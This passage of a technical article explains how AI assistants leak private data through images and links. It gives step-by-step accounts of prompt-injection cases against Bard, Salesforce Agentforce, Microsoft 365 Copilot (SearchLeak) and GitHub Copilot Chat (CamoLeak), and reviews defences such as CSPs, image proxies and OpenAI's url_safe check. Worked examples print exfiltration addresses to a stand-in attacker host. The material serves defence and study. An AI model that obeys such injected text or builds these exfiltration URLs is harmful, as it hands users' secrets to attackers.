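Microsoft published a broader account in July 2025, the month after the EchoLeak disclosure. Microsoft says it aims to make injections less likely to work, detect those that remain and prevent harm from any that succeed.

Microsoft uses a method called Spotlighting to help the model tell outside text from the user's instructions. Spotlighting can put random markers around the outside text, insert a special character between its words, or encode all of it in a form the model can still read. Microsoft also uses a classifier called Prompt Shields to detect injected instructions. Both defences are probabilistic, so they can miss attacks.

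Microsoft relies more on fixed rules for the third aim. A company can label sensitive files and stop Copilot from summarising them, so that an attacker's email cannot get their contents into a summary. When Copilot drafts an email, the user has to approve and send it. Microsoft also blocks known ways of sending data out. It blocked markdown images after Rehberger's report and later took similar steps against "certain untrusted links". It does not explain how its software identifies untrusted links, so outsiders cannot tell whether the rule is stricter than Google's.

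Microsoft also says that it responds to every report by looking for variants of the flaw, but EchoLeak casts doubt on this. A reference-style image is a close variant of the inline image that Rehberger reported in 2023, and it still got past Copilot's filter in January 2025. Rehberger's report concerned a different product, Bing Chat, and anticipating every variant is difficult. But a company that knew about the image leak could have found the reference style in the markdown specification.

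The policy also covers only what Microsoft accepts as a vulnerability. In October 2025 Checkmarx reported that text in an online article could make Copilot Chat send a developer's secret access key to an outside server through an image. The image never appeared on screen, but the request still went out. Microsoft closed the report on 4 November without a fix, though it passed the report to its engineers as a possible improvement. It said that the attack required several unusual actions by the user, did not work reliably and came with warnings, and that it expects people in such settings to review the code they run.

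### Checking addresses while the page is being built

Like a rule that blocks all images, an address check works best at the last step, when the renderer creates the element. By then the renderer has matched every label with its definition and turned bare addresses into links, so the check applies to exactly the links the renderer produces. It would have tested EchoLeak's reference-style image the same way as an inline one.

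Vercel Labs' *Markdown sanitizers* offers an open-source version of this check. Its package harden-react-markdown is a wrapper around react-markdown, the renderer in Escape's two cases. The developer lists the allowed prefixes for link and image addresses. React-markdown's default check would not be enough, because it only confirms that an address has a harmless scheme such as https, which the attacker's address also has.

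Suppose the employee's company allows pictures only from the folder where it stores its charts. The check would then give these results:

```
Allowed image prefix:  https://files.company.example/charts/

https://files.company.example/charts/sales.png              keep
https://files.company.example/fetch?url=pictures.example    remove
https://pictures.example/pixel.png?title=Budget%20review    remove
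```

The second address represents a relay on the company's own server, like the one in Teams. A rule that allowed the whole host would let it through, but a prefix that includes the folder would not. Without a slash after the host name, the prefix `https://files.company.example` also matches `https://files.company.example.pictures.example/`, which belongs to the attacker. The software should therefore compare the whole host name before checking the rest of the address.

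An app does not always control how its reply is finally rendered. A coding assistant may post its answer as a comment on GitHub or GitLab, which convert the markdown to HTML themselves. Vercel Labs has a second package for these cases, which takes in markdown and outputs cleaned markdown. Vercel Labs describes this as generally less secure than cleaning the final HTML and advises developers to use it only when someone else does the rendering. The other site will parse the cleaned text by its own rules, so the two programs can again differ in what they treat as a link.

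Vercel Labs warns that both packages have "subtle security properties" and tells developers to run their own tests. Escape points out that support consoles that replay customers' conversations to staff need the check too. If only the chat window has it, an image the customer never saw can still load when an employee opens the transcript.

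## Limiting which sites images may load from

With a Content Security Policy (CSP), the vendor gives the browser a list of the hosts that images may load from. This is easier to enforce than sanitization, because the browser only has to check the host in each image request, while a sanitizer has to recognise every way of writing an image. In EchoLeak, the CSP blocked image requests to outside hosts until the researchers found an allowed host that would forward them.

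### How the browser applies the list

Suppose the employee's assistant is at chat.company.example and its server sends this header, a short line of settings, along with the page:

```
Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' data:
    https://files.company.example https://*.search.example
```

The word "img-src" introduces the rule for images, and the rest is the allowlist:

| Entry | Images it permits |
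|---|---|
| `'self'` | Images from the page's own host, chat.company.example |
| `data:` | Images embedded in the page as data, which need no request |
| `https://files.company.example` | Images from exactly this host |
| `https://*.search.example` | Images from any host whose name ends in .search.example, such as www.search.example |

Each time the page needs an image, the browser works out the full address and compares its host with the entries. If one matches, the browser sends the request. If none does, it drops the request before contacting the host and records an error in its developer console. Three addresses would give these results:

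```
https://files.company.example/charts/sales.png              load
https://pictures.example/pixel.png?title=Budget%20review    refuse
https://www.search.example/by-image?picture=
    https://pictures.example/Budget%20review.png            load
```

The first address points to an ordinary chart on a listed host, and the second points to the attacker's image from the worked example. The third contains the attacker's address and the meeting title, but the browser loads it because its host, www.search.example, is on the list. If that site fetches whatever address it receives, the title reaches the attacker anyway.

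An entry can also include a path. With `https://files.company.example/charts/`, the browser loads only files in that folder. But the browser doesn't check the parameters after the question mark, so an attacker can always add data to an address on a permitted host. This causes a leak only if the attacker can find out what the host received.

The image rule also covers background pictures in style sheets and the preview picture of a video. It does not cover the video itself or a page embedded in the chat. Each of those follows its own rule or, if that is missing, a general one called default-src. If the header has neither, the browser loads that content from anywhere. The image rule does not affect ordinary links.

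### What the list adds to a text filter

A CSP avoids mismatches between filter and renderer because the browser applies it after rendering. An inline image, a reference-style image and an HTML image tag all lead to the same request, so the browser treats them the same way. The browser checks each request as it occurs, so the policy also works while the model is still generating its reply.

Google AI Studio had no Content Security Policy (CSP) when it leaked data through an HTML image tag in 2024, according to Embrace The Red's *Google AI Studio*. A CSP that didn't allow images from researcher Johann Rehberger's server would have blocked the request.

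Outsiders can also inspect a CSP, since the server sends it to every visitor and anyone can read it in the browser's developer tools. Researchers can search the list of allowed hosts for a weak entry, whereas they have to work out the rules of a filter on the vendor's server by trial and error. Customers can check the list before buying the product. Attackers can read it too, so a vendor should assume that someone will examine every host on it.

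### The first lists: Bing Chat and VS Code

Embrace The Red lists the four hosts that Microsoft's 2023 CSP for Bing Chat allowed: th.bing.com, www.bing.com, edgeservices.bing.com and r.bing.com. Bing Chat could therefore still display pictures it had created for the user.

GitHub made a similar change a year later to Copilot Chat in VS Code, Microsoft's code editor. The attacker's text could be in a comment in a source file. When a developer asked Copilot to explain the file, the model put details from the chat into an image address. Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat* records that Rehberger reported this on 25 February 2024. GitHub replied on 6 March that the bug was valid and one it was already tracking. It confirmed a fix on 12 June.

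Accounts of the fix differ. Rehberger thought that Copilot Chat no longer displayed any markdown images. Willison, in *GitHub Copilot Chat*, wrote that GitHub had disabled only images from untrusted domains. Vulners' *Source Code and data exfiltration via Github Copilot*, an undated summary of a GitHub report, also describes a fix that allows images only from trusted domains and shows a warning before links open, but it may concern a different report. Willison's version is probably right. Rehberger tested with an image on his own server, which would have been blocked under either rule.

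An app that checks addresses against its own list, rather than relying on a browser's CSP, can get the comparison wrong. VS Code had a list of trusted domains, including Microsoft's and GitHub's sites, from which Copilot's tool for fetching web pages could load pages without the user's confirmation. According to GitHub's *Safeguarding VS Code against prompt injections*, the software matched a text pattern against the whole address instead of just the host, so an address on any server passed if its path contained ".github.com".

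A GitHub researcher used this mistake to send an access token from a file on the developer's computer to an outside server. The VS Code team then stopped using the list for the fetch tool and made it ask for confirmation before opening any new address. The same trick would not work for an image restricted by a CSP, because the browser extracts the host from the address before comparing it.

### Google Bard: the attacker's program on a Google host

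Google already had a CSP on Bard, the chatbot it later renamed Gemini, when Rehberger tested it in September 2023. Bard had just gained access to users' Gmail, Drive and Docs. An attacker could share a document with someone without their consent, and instructions in the document would take effect if Bard read it while answering a question.

Bard turned image markdown into HTML, but the CSP blocked an image on Rehberger's own server. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* reports that the policy permitted `*.google.com` and `*.googleusercontent.com`. These wildcards covered Google Apps Script, a service that lets anyone write small programs and run them on Google's servers by opening a URL.

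Rehberger wrote a script that copied the parameters of each request into a Google Doc, and found a setting that let it accept requests from people who had not logged in. The instructions in his shared document then had Bard put the first 20 words of the conversation into an image address on script.google.com. The browser sent the request because it was going to a Google host, and the script copied the words into the Google Doc.

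The request never had to leave Google's network. Google owned the host, but Rehberger controlled the program that received the request and could read what it recorded.

He needed ten tries to get Bard to write the address correctly, and he had to include several examples of where the words should go, which other chatbots had not needed. But once the text worked, he could put it in any number of shared documents.

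Rehberger reported the flaw on 19 September, and Google confirmed the fix a month later. The CSP had not changed and images still loaded, so he guessed that Google was now filtering out addresses with inserted data. A CSP cannot permit every Google host except one, so to block a single host Google would have had to replace the wildcard with a list of every host that Bard's images came from.

### Salesforce Agentforce: a permitted domain for $5

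A vendor can also lose control of a host on its list. Salesforce's software stores companies' customer records, and its Agentforce AI agents can search them. *ForcedLeak* (Nytro, 2025) reproduces a report by Noma Labs, whose security researchers found a way to extract data from Agentforce.

The attack began with a public web form that companies use to collect enquiries from possible customers, or leads. Most fields accepted 80 characters or fewer, but the description field accepted 42,000, enough for detailed instructions. Salesforce stored the submission as an ordinary record. When an employee later asked the agent to deal with that lead, the agent also followed the attacker's instructions to retrieve the email addresses of the company's leads and produce an image whose URL contained them.

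Salesforce's CSP should have blocked the image. The policy allowed 22 host patterns, 15 of them with wildcards, and many had names related to Salesforce or its messaging service, Slack. One was `*.my-salesforce-cms.com`, a domain whose registration Salesforce had let expire. Noma bought the domain for $5. After that, browsers sent Noma any image request for it, because a CSP allows domains by name, regardless of who owns them.

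Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025 and published it on 25 September, after Salesforce had taken back the domain. According to Willison's *ForcedLeak*, Salesforce audited and corrected the CSP, then added a feature called Trusted URLs that stops agents from producing links to unapproved sites. Trusted URLs also covers ordinary links, which the image rule does not restrict.

Taking back the expired domain would probably not have been enough, because the header that Noma published also permitted `*.amazonaws.com`, which includes storage that any customer of Amazon's cloud service can rent. Customers can log the requests for their own files, including the parameters, so an attacker might not have needed the expired domain. Noma does not report trying this.

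Companies that use Trusted URLs now have to maintain their own lists. An administrator adds each outside address in Salesforce's settings. PromptArmor advises against wildcards that cover sites where users can post content, and recommends allowing images only from sites whose images the company intends to show.

### SearchLeak: a fast image and a relay

An allowlist entry can be dangerous even when its owner is trustworthy and still controls the host, as happened with Bing in 2026. Taler describes every step of SearchLeak, the attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot's search page that exposed the title of an email.

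1. The attacker sends the victim a link to Copilot's real search page. A parameter in the link contains the search query, so that people can share or bookmark a search. Copilot treated this text as instructions and acted on it as soon as the page opened. Varonis calls this parameter-to-prompt injection. The victim typed nothing, and the link led to a genuine Microsoft site, so a filter that judged links by their host had no reason to block it.

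2. The instructions have Copilot search the victim's mailbox and write an HTML image tag with an email's title in the address.

3. The browser starts to load the image while Copilot is still writing. Microsoft's sanitizer put the reply inside an HTML code element, which makes a browser show markup as text, but it did so only after Copilot had finished. Until then, the page contained a working image tag.

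4. The browser checks the address against the CSP. The address is on Bing, which the policy permits through the entry `*.bing.com`, so the request goes out.

5. Bing's image search receives the request. This feature lets people search with a picture instead of words, and it accepts the picture's web address. The address in the request points to the attacker's server and has the email title in its path.

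6. Bing's server fetches that address in order to analyse the picture, and the title appears in the attacker's log.

Bing's server sent the last request, so the victim's browser could not apply the CSP to it. In this kind of flaw, called server-side request forgery, an attacker gets someone else's server to send a request the attacker has chosen. The attacker's log showed Bing's network address instead of the victim's, but it still contained the title.

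Varonis needed both the early image and the relay:

| When the sanitizer ran | Where the image address pointed | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Before display | The attacker's server | The tag appears as text and nothing loads |
| Before display | Bing, with the attacker's address inside | The tag appears as text and nothing loads |
| After display began | The attacker's server | The CSP blocks the request |
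| After display began | Bing, with the attacker's address inside | The title reaches the attacker |

While a reply was streaming, Copilot had the CSP but no sanitizer, and once a request had gone to Bing it had neither. The two never applied to the same dangerous image at the same time, although Microsoft may have regarded them as backups for each other.

A shorter list might not have helped, because the image search was on www.bing.com, one of the four hosts Microsoft had listed individually for Bing Chat in 2023. To allow Bing's pictures but block the image search, Microsoft would have had to limit the entry to particular paths or serve the pictures from a host used only for them.

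The EchoLeak researchers had already used the Teams relay in the same way, so Microsoft had a recent example of the problem. Checking every permitted host for features that fetch outside addresses could have found the image search too. That would have been a large job for `*.bing.com`, since the wildcard covers every service Microsoft runs under that domain.

Varonis says the attacker could also have reached meeting details and company files. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* explains that Copilot could search whatever the signed-in user had permission to open. A login code in an email's subject line is often valid for several minutes, which gives an attacker watching the log time to use it.

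Microsoft published its advisory for the flaw (CVE-2026-42824), *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), on 4 June, and Varonis published its account on 15 June. Microsoft rated the flaw critical on its own scale. On CVSS, the standard scale for security flaws, it scored 6.5 out of 10, a medium rating, partly because the victim had to click a link. According to The Next Web, Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers and found no evidence that anyone had exploited it.

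Taler had used the same kind of link before in Reprompt, an attack on the consumer version of Copilot. He reported it in August 2025, and Microsoft patched it in January 2026. Varonis was surprised that the method also worked on the business version, which was supposed to have stronger protections.

Microsoft could have stopped the SearchLeak attack by fixing any one of the three weaknesses it relied on. Requiring the user to confirm a query that came from a link would have stopped this attack, but instructions in an email could still have made Copilot produce the same image. Sanitizing each piece of the reply before displaying it, or closing the route through Bing, would protect against both. Varonis recommends sanitizing output as it is displayed and treating any permitted host that fetches user-supplied URLs as a possible route for leaking data.

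### Which hosts are safe to permit

A vendor can safely permit a host only if an attacker cannot learn what requests the host receives. Recognising the company's name is not enough to establish this, because Google, Amazon and Microsoft all offer services that an attacker can use.

The host must not fetch addresses that other people supply, as features such as image search, link previews, web page translation and image resizing do. The vendor has to check the whole host for such features and, if the list uses a wildcard, every host under that name. It also has to repeat the check from time to time, because another team may add such a feature years later without knowing that the host is on a chatbot's list.

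Attackers must not be able to read an allowed host's request logs. This rules out most services where customers run programs and many where they store files. Public view counts can also leak private data. If a site shows a count for each image, an attacker can upload several images, have the model display one chosen according to the private data, and see which count goes up.

The owner has to keep control of the name. Expired registrations are fairly easy to find because anyone can look up a domain's status, but abandoned subdomains are harder to spot. A company may point a name such as images.company.example at rented cloud storage, then cancel the storage and forget the name. With some cloud services, a stranger can then claim the same storage and receive every request sent to it. Removing a site from the allowed list as soon as the product stops using it prevents both problems.

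A server can answer a request by redirecting the browser to another address. Under a CSP, the browser also checks the new address, so a redirect from a permitted host to pictures.example fails. But after a redirect, the browser ignores any path in the matching entry and compares only the host. If a vendor had permitted just one folder on a host in order to exclude a relay elsewhere on it, a redirect from any permitted address could still lead to the relay.

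Redirects are more dangerous when the app does the checking. A renderer that compares an image's address with a list checks only the first address, and the browser then follows any redirect unless a CSP blocks it. VS Code's list of trusted domains included aka.ms, Microsoft's link shortener, which works by redirecting. Outsiders cannot normally create aka.ms links, but many other trusted sites have pages that will forward a visitor to any address. OpenAI also cites redirects as a reason not to rely on lists of trusted sites.

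The easiest host to check is one that the vendor sets up only for its own images, with no user accounts, redirects or other features. Such a host can't supply images from other websites. A vendor that wants to display those while keeping its list of allowed hosts short can fetch them through its own server, as GitHub does with its image proxy, Camo. However, Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes how GitHub's own infrastructure was used to bypass the CSP.

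## Loading images through a proxy

An image proxy lets a chat product show pictures from anywhere on the web without adding their hosts to its allowlist. GitHub was running its proxy, Camo, long before it had an AI assistant. In 2025 a researcher used Camo to get secrets out of GitHub's assistant, Copilot Chat, one character at a time.

### What a proxy hides

Suppose the employee's assistant loads its pictures through a proxy at images.company.example. When the reply contains the image with the meeting title, the app puts the attacker's address inside an address on the proxy:

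```
https://images.company.example/fetch?url=
    https%3A%2F%2Fpictures.example%2Fpixel.png%3Ftitle%3DBudget%2520review
```

The browser sends its request to the proxy. The proxy decodes the inner address and sends a request of its own to pictures.example, so the attacker's log gets a slightly different entry from the one in the worked example:

```
198.51.100.20 [05/Dec/2026:10:14:02 +0000]
"GET /pixel.png?title=Budget%20review HTTP/1.1" 200 "Image proxy"
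```

| What the outside server can learn | Direct loading | Loading through the proxy |
|---|---|---|
| Network address | The employee's | The proxy's |
| Type of browser | Hers | None, only the proxy's name |
| Cookies that the outside site set earlier | Yes, if her browser allows it | No |
| Time of the request | Yes | Yes, unless the proxy already has a copy |
| The full image address, with the meeting title | Yes | Yes |

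The cookies stay private because a browser sends a site's cookies only to that site, and here the browser contacts only the proxy. Without the cookies, the attacker can't recognise the employee from an earlier visit. But the attacker still receives the meeting title, because it is in the address the proxy uses to fetch the picture.

Image proxies were designed for problems other than this kind of leak. GitHub's *Sidejack Prevention Phase 3* explains that GitHub built Camo because browsers showed a warning when a secure page contained an image from an insecure address. In January 2014, GitHub began sending images from secure addresses through Camo too. Its *Proxying User Images* (2014) gave privacy as a reason, since other companies would no longer receive information about users' browsers. GitLab recommends a similar proxy to customers who run its software themselves, because someone could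 put an image in a comment to collect readers' network addresses. That person writes the image address before any reader sees it, so the address can't contain the reader's secrets.

Most of a proxy's other safety checks happen too late to prevent a leak. By default, Camo rejects images over 5 megabytes, times out after ten seconds and follows no more than four redirects, according to its documentation on GitHub. It also accepts only certain file types. These rules protect the proxy and the reader from bad files, but Camo can check a file's size and type only after the outside server responds, and by then that server has already received the image's address.

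A proxy that fetches any address given to it can relay data to an attacker. The Teams service in EchoLeak worked this way, and attackers were still finding such services in 2026. In the ReLeak attack that used an image address, Simonovich writes, the browser's request reached the attacker's server through Bing. Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, quotes the researchers as saying that "too little progress has been made" in the year since they exposed a similar flaw.

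### How Camo signs addresses

Camo fetches an address only if it comes with a valid signature, a code that GitHub calculates with a secret key. Suppose a programmer adds a picture from pictures.example to a README, the page that introduces a project:

1. GitHub's server converts the README from markdown to HTML and finds the outside image.

2. It calculates a signature from the image's full address and the secret key.

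3. It writes the address in hexadecimal, which uses two characters from 0–9 and a–f for each original character. This keeps punctuation in the address from causing trouble. It does not hide anything, because anyone can reverse it.

4. It puts the signature and the encoded address into a new address on Camo's host, and uses that in the HTML.

5. A reader opens the README, and her browser requests the image from Camo. GitHub's Content Security Policy permits this because the host belongs to GitHub.

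6. Camo decodes the outside address and calculates the signature again with its own copy of the key. If the two signatures differ, it refuses the request without contacting the outside server.

7. If they match, Camo fetches the picture and passes it to the browser.

For a picture called map.png, the two addresses look like this:

```
Original:  https://pictures.example/map.png

Proxied:   https://camo.githubusercontent.com/<signature>/
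           68747470733a2f2f70696374757265732e6578616d706c652f6d61702e706e67
```

The signature is an HMAC, short for hash-based message authentication code:

```
signature = HMAC(secret key, image address)
```

The same key and address always give the same signature. Changing one character of the address gives a completely different signature, which nobody has a practical way to work out without the key. In the published version of Camo, the signature has 40 hexadecimal characters, which allows about 10^48 possibilities, far too many to guess.

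Suppose an attacker uses text to instruct a model to add the meeting title to a Camo address. The model can write the title in hexadecimal, but it cannot sign the new address because it does not have the key. If it copies the signature from another image, the signature will not match the new address, so Camo will reject the request and the title will not reach pictures.example.

This works only if the chat app does not sign the model's images itself. If the app treated each reply like a README, GitHub's server would sign the address of the image with the meeting title and so allow the leak. Copilot Chat evidently did not sign images in its replies, because the attack on it needed addresses that GitHub had signed beforehand.

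According to its documentation, GitHub originally used the signatures so that it could clear stored copies, ban addresses and limit the rate of requests. Despair Labs' *Introducing hopscotch, a tiny image proxy* (2014), which describes a proxy modelled on Camo, gives another common reason: strangers cannot use the proxy for their own purposes, because only the developer's application can create working addresses. A valid signature proves only that the application created the address, not that it should have.

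### CamoLeak: one signed address for each character

Omer Mayraz of Legit Security found a way around the signatures in June 2025 and reported it to GitHub through HackerOne, a service for reporting security flaws. His attack, which he called CamoLeak, worked against the version of Copilot Chat on GitHub's website. That version answers questions about the page the user has open and can read the user's private projects.

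The attacker's text was in a hidden comment, which GitHub allows in the description of a pull request (a proposal to change a project's code). The comment doesn't appear on the page or in the notification the project's owner gets, but Copilot still read it. When Mayraz logged in as a different user and asked Copilot to explain the pull request, Copilot followed the hidden instructions with that user's permissions.

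He first built a version that needed one click. Copilot read a file from a private project, encoded it and added it to a link's address. To remove the click, he needed an image, but GitHub's policy blocked images from his server, and Copilot could not sign new Camo addresses.

Mayraz prepared the addresses he needed in advance. He put a set of images on his own server, one for each letter and symbol that might appear in a secret. GitHub has a public interface that programs can use to convert markdown to HTML, and it replaces every outside image address with a signed Camo address. He used it to get a valid address for each character, then put the list in the hidden comment. The instructions described the task as a game in which Copilot had to spell out the secret text with these images.

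To spell "Budget review", Copilot would display thirteen images, starting with the ones for B, u and d. The browser would request them from Camo in that order. Camo would find each signature valid and fetch the image from Mayraz's server, where the log entries, read in order, would spell out the title. No single address contained private data, and GitHub had signed them all before the victim opened the page.

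Each image was a single transparent pixel, so the victim saw nothing unusual. Browsers and proxies keep copies of images they have already loaded, which caused a problem with repeated letters. The images for the second and third "e" in "Budget review" would have come from a stored copy, and the log would have shown "Budget rviw". Mayraz had Copilot add a new random number to the end of each Camo address so that each one looked like a different image.

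The random number did not invalidate the signature, so the signature must not have covered that part of the address. Camo presumably also left the number out of its request to the outside server. Otherwise Mayraz could have put the secret there and would not have needed a list of characters.

He demonstrated the attack by extracting the description of an unpatched security flaw from a private project. He also had Copilot search all of a victim's code for "AWS_KEY", a common label for keys to Amazon's cloud service, and send him what it found. He gives no success rate, and Copilot would have had to copy hundreds of long addresses without a mistake to send a long secret. But a cloud key is short and needs fewer addresses, and the instructions stayed in the pull request, where they could affect anyone else who asked Copilot about it.

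Legit Security rates CamoLeak 9.6 out of 10 on the CVSS scale, compared with 6.5 for SearchLeak. Some accounts mistakenly identify CamoLeak as CVE-2025-59145, which belongs to malicious code in a JavaScript package (MITRE, *color-name@2.0.1 contains malware after npm account takeover*, 2025).

### Why GitHub removed the images

GitHub told Mayraz on 14 August 2025 that it had fixed the flaw. Legit Security says GitHub fixed it by turning off all images in Copilot Chat. SecurityWeek's *GitHub Copilot Chat Flaw Leaked Data From Private Repositories* reports that GitHub wrote that it no longer allowed the use of Camo to leak users' sensitive information. Both descriptions can be true, because a reply without images causes no requests to Camo. The attack became public on 8 October, the date of the earliest article listed in the OECD's *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and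 Secrets*.

GitHub has not published its reasons for removing images instead of repairing the proxy. The likeliest is that Camo was not broken. It received valid addresses and fetched ordinary pictures, as it does for millions of READMEs, and the secret was only in the order of the requests. The obvious repairs would all have been incomplete or would have affected the rest of the site:

| Possible repair | Why it would not have been enough |
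|---|---|
| Stop signing addresses through the public interface | An attacker could put the images in a README and copy the signed addresses from the page |
| Refuse Camo addresses with anything added at the end | An attacker could prepare several images for each common letter |
| Limit the number of images per page | Short secrets need few images, and many READMEs have rows of small status badges |
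| Change the secret key | An attacker could get new signatures the same way, and GitHub would have to update every stored page |

GitHub could have given Copilot Chat its own proxy with a separate key, so that Camo addresses from a README would have failed in the chat. But GitHub would still have had to decide which images the new proxy should sign, for a feature that few people need when they ask about code. Removing images from the chat took one change to one product and did not affect READMEs.

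Users can still give Copilot Chat pictures after the fix. GitHub's *Copilot vision is generally available* (2026) announced in July that people could attach images and PDFs to their questions, including on GitHub's website. An attached picture goes from the user to GitHub, so the model does not write an outside address for it. Mayraz's one-click version did not use images, and Legit Security does not mention any change to links.

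### Proxies that would resist CamoLeak

In their table of EchoLeak's steps, Reddy and Gujral say that a strict CSP or an image proxy would block an image hosted on an attacker's server. However, CamoLeak succeeded against a site that had both. To stop such attacks, a proxy has to ensure that private data cannot affect which requests the outside server receives or when it receives them.

| Design | Address containing the meeting title | One prepared image per character | Main cost |
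|---|---|---|---|
| Fetch any address | Leaks | Leaks | No protection beyond the user's identity |
| Sign any address that a user submits, as Camo does | Blocked | Leaks | Every image needs a signature first |
| Copy all images before private data arrives | Blocked | Blocked | Fetches many images that nobody will see |
| Show only images already in storage | Blocked | Blocked | Most of the web's pictures are missing |
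| Sign only images from trusted sources | Blocked | Blocked, if attackers cannot add to the sources | Pictures from strangers are missing |

**Copying images in advance.** When the assistant opens the page about conference venues, the vendor's server could download every picture on it before the model reads the text. It would replace each image address with a short name such as "image 7", and the model could use only these names to include images in its reply. The attacker's server would get one request for each picture, whatever the employee's next meeting was called. Even if the page contained a picture for every letter, the attacker's server would get one request per letter, which would reveal nothing about the meeting's name.

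The vendor has to download all the pictures or choose among them by a fixed rule, such as taking the first twenty. If the model chose after reading the inbox, its choice could leak data. The vendor must also keep the copies for as long as the conversation can display them. If a copy expired after an hour and the server fetched the picture again when the employee reopened the chat, the attacker would see which pictures the reply contained.

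An ordinary cache, where a server keeps recent copies to save time, is not reliable enough for this. GitHub's *About anonymized image URLs* advises people whose images change often to have their servers send a "no-cache" instruction, so that Camo picks up the new version. An attacker's server can send the same instruction. The page also gives a single command that deletes an image from Camo's cache, so Camo has to fetch it again.

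Downloading everything also uses storage and bandwidth and slows the first answer a little. None of the chat vendors covered so far describes doing this for images. Downloading everything would not protect the request for the page itself if the model had already read the inbox.

**Showing only stored images.** A stricter proxy never contacts an outside server and shows an image only if the vendor already has a copy. GitHub does this with videos. It does not support videos hosted on other sites, so every video address on GitHub leads to a file that someone uploaded there. ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode applies the same principle to web pages.

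The outside server gets no request, so the attacker gains nothing from an invented address or a prepared list. The vendor must still keep view counts private, as on any permitted host. The assistant also has far fewer pictures to choose from. A product photo posted this morning would be missing, as would most pictures on obscure sites. This may hardly matter for an assistant that answers questions about a company's own documents.

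**Signing only trusted sources.** A vendor could keep Camo's method but sign only images from sources it trusts. The employee's company, for instance, might sign only pictures from its own chart folder. The attacker could not get a signed alphabet without being able to add files to that folder. Trust has to depend on who can write to a source, which is not always just its owner. For example, GitHub owns the page that shows a pull request, but a stranger can write the description.

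No chat vendor covered so far documents such signatures. The nearest equivalent is Claude's image search, in which the model picks from a list of results. That list is less selective than a company's chart folder because an attacker can try to get pictures into a public search engine.

Camo's signatures also work for anyone who has them. GitHub warns that any person who receives one of its image addresses can view the image, and this let Mayraz prepare his list in one account and use it in another. A vendor could tie each signature to a single conversation and give it an end date:

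```
signature = HMAC(secret key, conversation number + end date + image address)
```

If the vendor tied signatures to a conversation, a list that the attacker prepared elsewhere would fail in the employee's chat. But the attacker could get around this if the vendor signed the pictures on every page the model read. The attacker would put the prepared pictures on the page about conference venues, and the vendor would sign them all for the employee's conversation before the model started its reply. Tying signatures to a conversation therefore helps only if the vendor also limits which sources it signs or copies the pictures in advance.

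## Checking each address on a server before loading it

OpenAI's URL safety check runs on each address only when ChatGPT is about to load it, whereas GitHub may sign an image's address long before any chat uses it. The protection therefore depends entirely on the rule on OpenAI's server. OpenAI kept that rule secret for two years, while outsiders worked out parts of it and bypassed it several times. In January 2026, OpenAI published the reasoning behind a stricter rule.

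### The first version, December 2023

The check appeared in ChatGPT's web version a day after Rehberger had used an image to extract a consenting volunteer's conversation in a live demonstration. In the worked example, it would go like this:

1. ChatGPT's server sends the summary of conference venues to the employee's browser piece by piece.

2. When the page reaches the image, it does not create an image element yet. It sends the image's address to url_safe, an endpoint (an address at which a server answers requests from programs).

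3. OpenAI's server applies its rule and answers true or false.

4. If the answer is true, the page creates the element and the browser fetches the picture. If it is false, the page leaves the picture out and the browser never contacts the outside server.

```
Request:  https://chat.openai.com/backend-api/conversation/<id>/url_safe
              ?url=https://pictures.example/pixel.png?title=Budget%20review

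Reply:    {"safe":false}
```

Embrace The Red shows this exchange for an image address on Rehberger's own server that had an email address as its parameter. The reply was `false` and the image did not load. OpenAI learns nothing new from the query, since its own model wrote the image address.

Willison (2023), in *21st December 2023*, welcomed the change but found it "a bit weird" that OpenAI had not simply blocked images from outside domains. Checking addresses on a server allows useful images from those domains to load. OpenAI can also change the rule without changing the page, and search the queries for signs of an attack.

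This arrangement was weak because it relied on the page to request a result for each address and act on it. Every other app needed its own version of the check, and the iPhone app did not have one yet. Rehberger suspected that OpenAI had put the check in the page so that replies could keep streaming. He thought a check on the server would be better because it would cover every app at once.

He also disliked that the rule was secret, so outsiders could not inspect it as they can a Content Security Policy. Some images from unrelated sites still loaded. The server accepted `/img/a.png` on his own site but refused `/img/d.png`, for reasons he could not work out. He guessed that OpenAI might be looking addresses up in Bing's index, and hoped that a language model was not making the decision alone.

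### What outsiders learned about the secret rule

A rule is hard to keep secret when anyone with an account can submit an address and see the result. The security company Imperva tested addresses this way systematically, not long after ChatGPT gained its memory feature. Imperva's *From ChatBot To SpyBot* describes a rule that searches for the address in the user's own text and treats certain domains differently.

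| Address sent to url_safe | Answer Imperva got |
|---|---|
| Any address that appeared in text the user had supplied | Safe |
| A bare domain, such as `https://pictures.example` | Safe |
| A subdomain, such as `https://budget-review.pictures.example` | Not safe |
| Any subdomain of google.com | Safe |
| Any subdomain, path or parameters on openai.com | Safe |

The first row makes sense, because the model cannot have added private data to an address that the user already typed. Imperva thought OpenAI refused unfamiliar subdomains because an attacker can put data in them, as in the third row.

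But the server compared plain strings. Imperva found that the text did not have to be a valid address and could match any part of the conversation. Both a full address and just the beginning of it therefore passed, which gave an attacker some choice over what the outside server received.

The server also treated custom instructions, the standing preferences that ChatGPT applies to every chat, as the user's text. Imperva was studying these instructions because it had found flaws that could let an attacker change them. Text in the user's part of a conversation may also have come from someone else, as in Samoilenko's copy-and-paste attack.

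Tenable later saw signs of a more complicated rule. Tenable's *HackedGPT* lists the domain, subdomain, parameters and conversation so far among the things the server seemed to consider. By then the server checked links as well as images, and ChatGPT left out any link that failed.

Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) reports that the server always approved addresses on bing.com. Each Bing search result has a bing.com address that forwards the visitor to the website, so anyone whose site appears in Bing has a bing.com address leading to it. The server approved these forwarding addresses, and the images loaded. The links are fixed, so the researchers could not add data to them and instead leaked text by choosing among links prepared in advance.

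Tenable sent OpenAI details of the flaw on 10 December 2024 and had asked for updates six times by 4 March 2025. OpenAI still had not fixed it when Tenable published its advisory.

### Two accepted domains with readable logs

Rehberger found a more direct route, which could send a whole passage at once. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* sets out three conditions for it:

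1. The server must treat a site as safe even when the model has made up the rest of the address.

2. The site must accept data in a GET request.

3. The attacker must be able to see what the site received, for example in a log.

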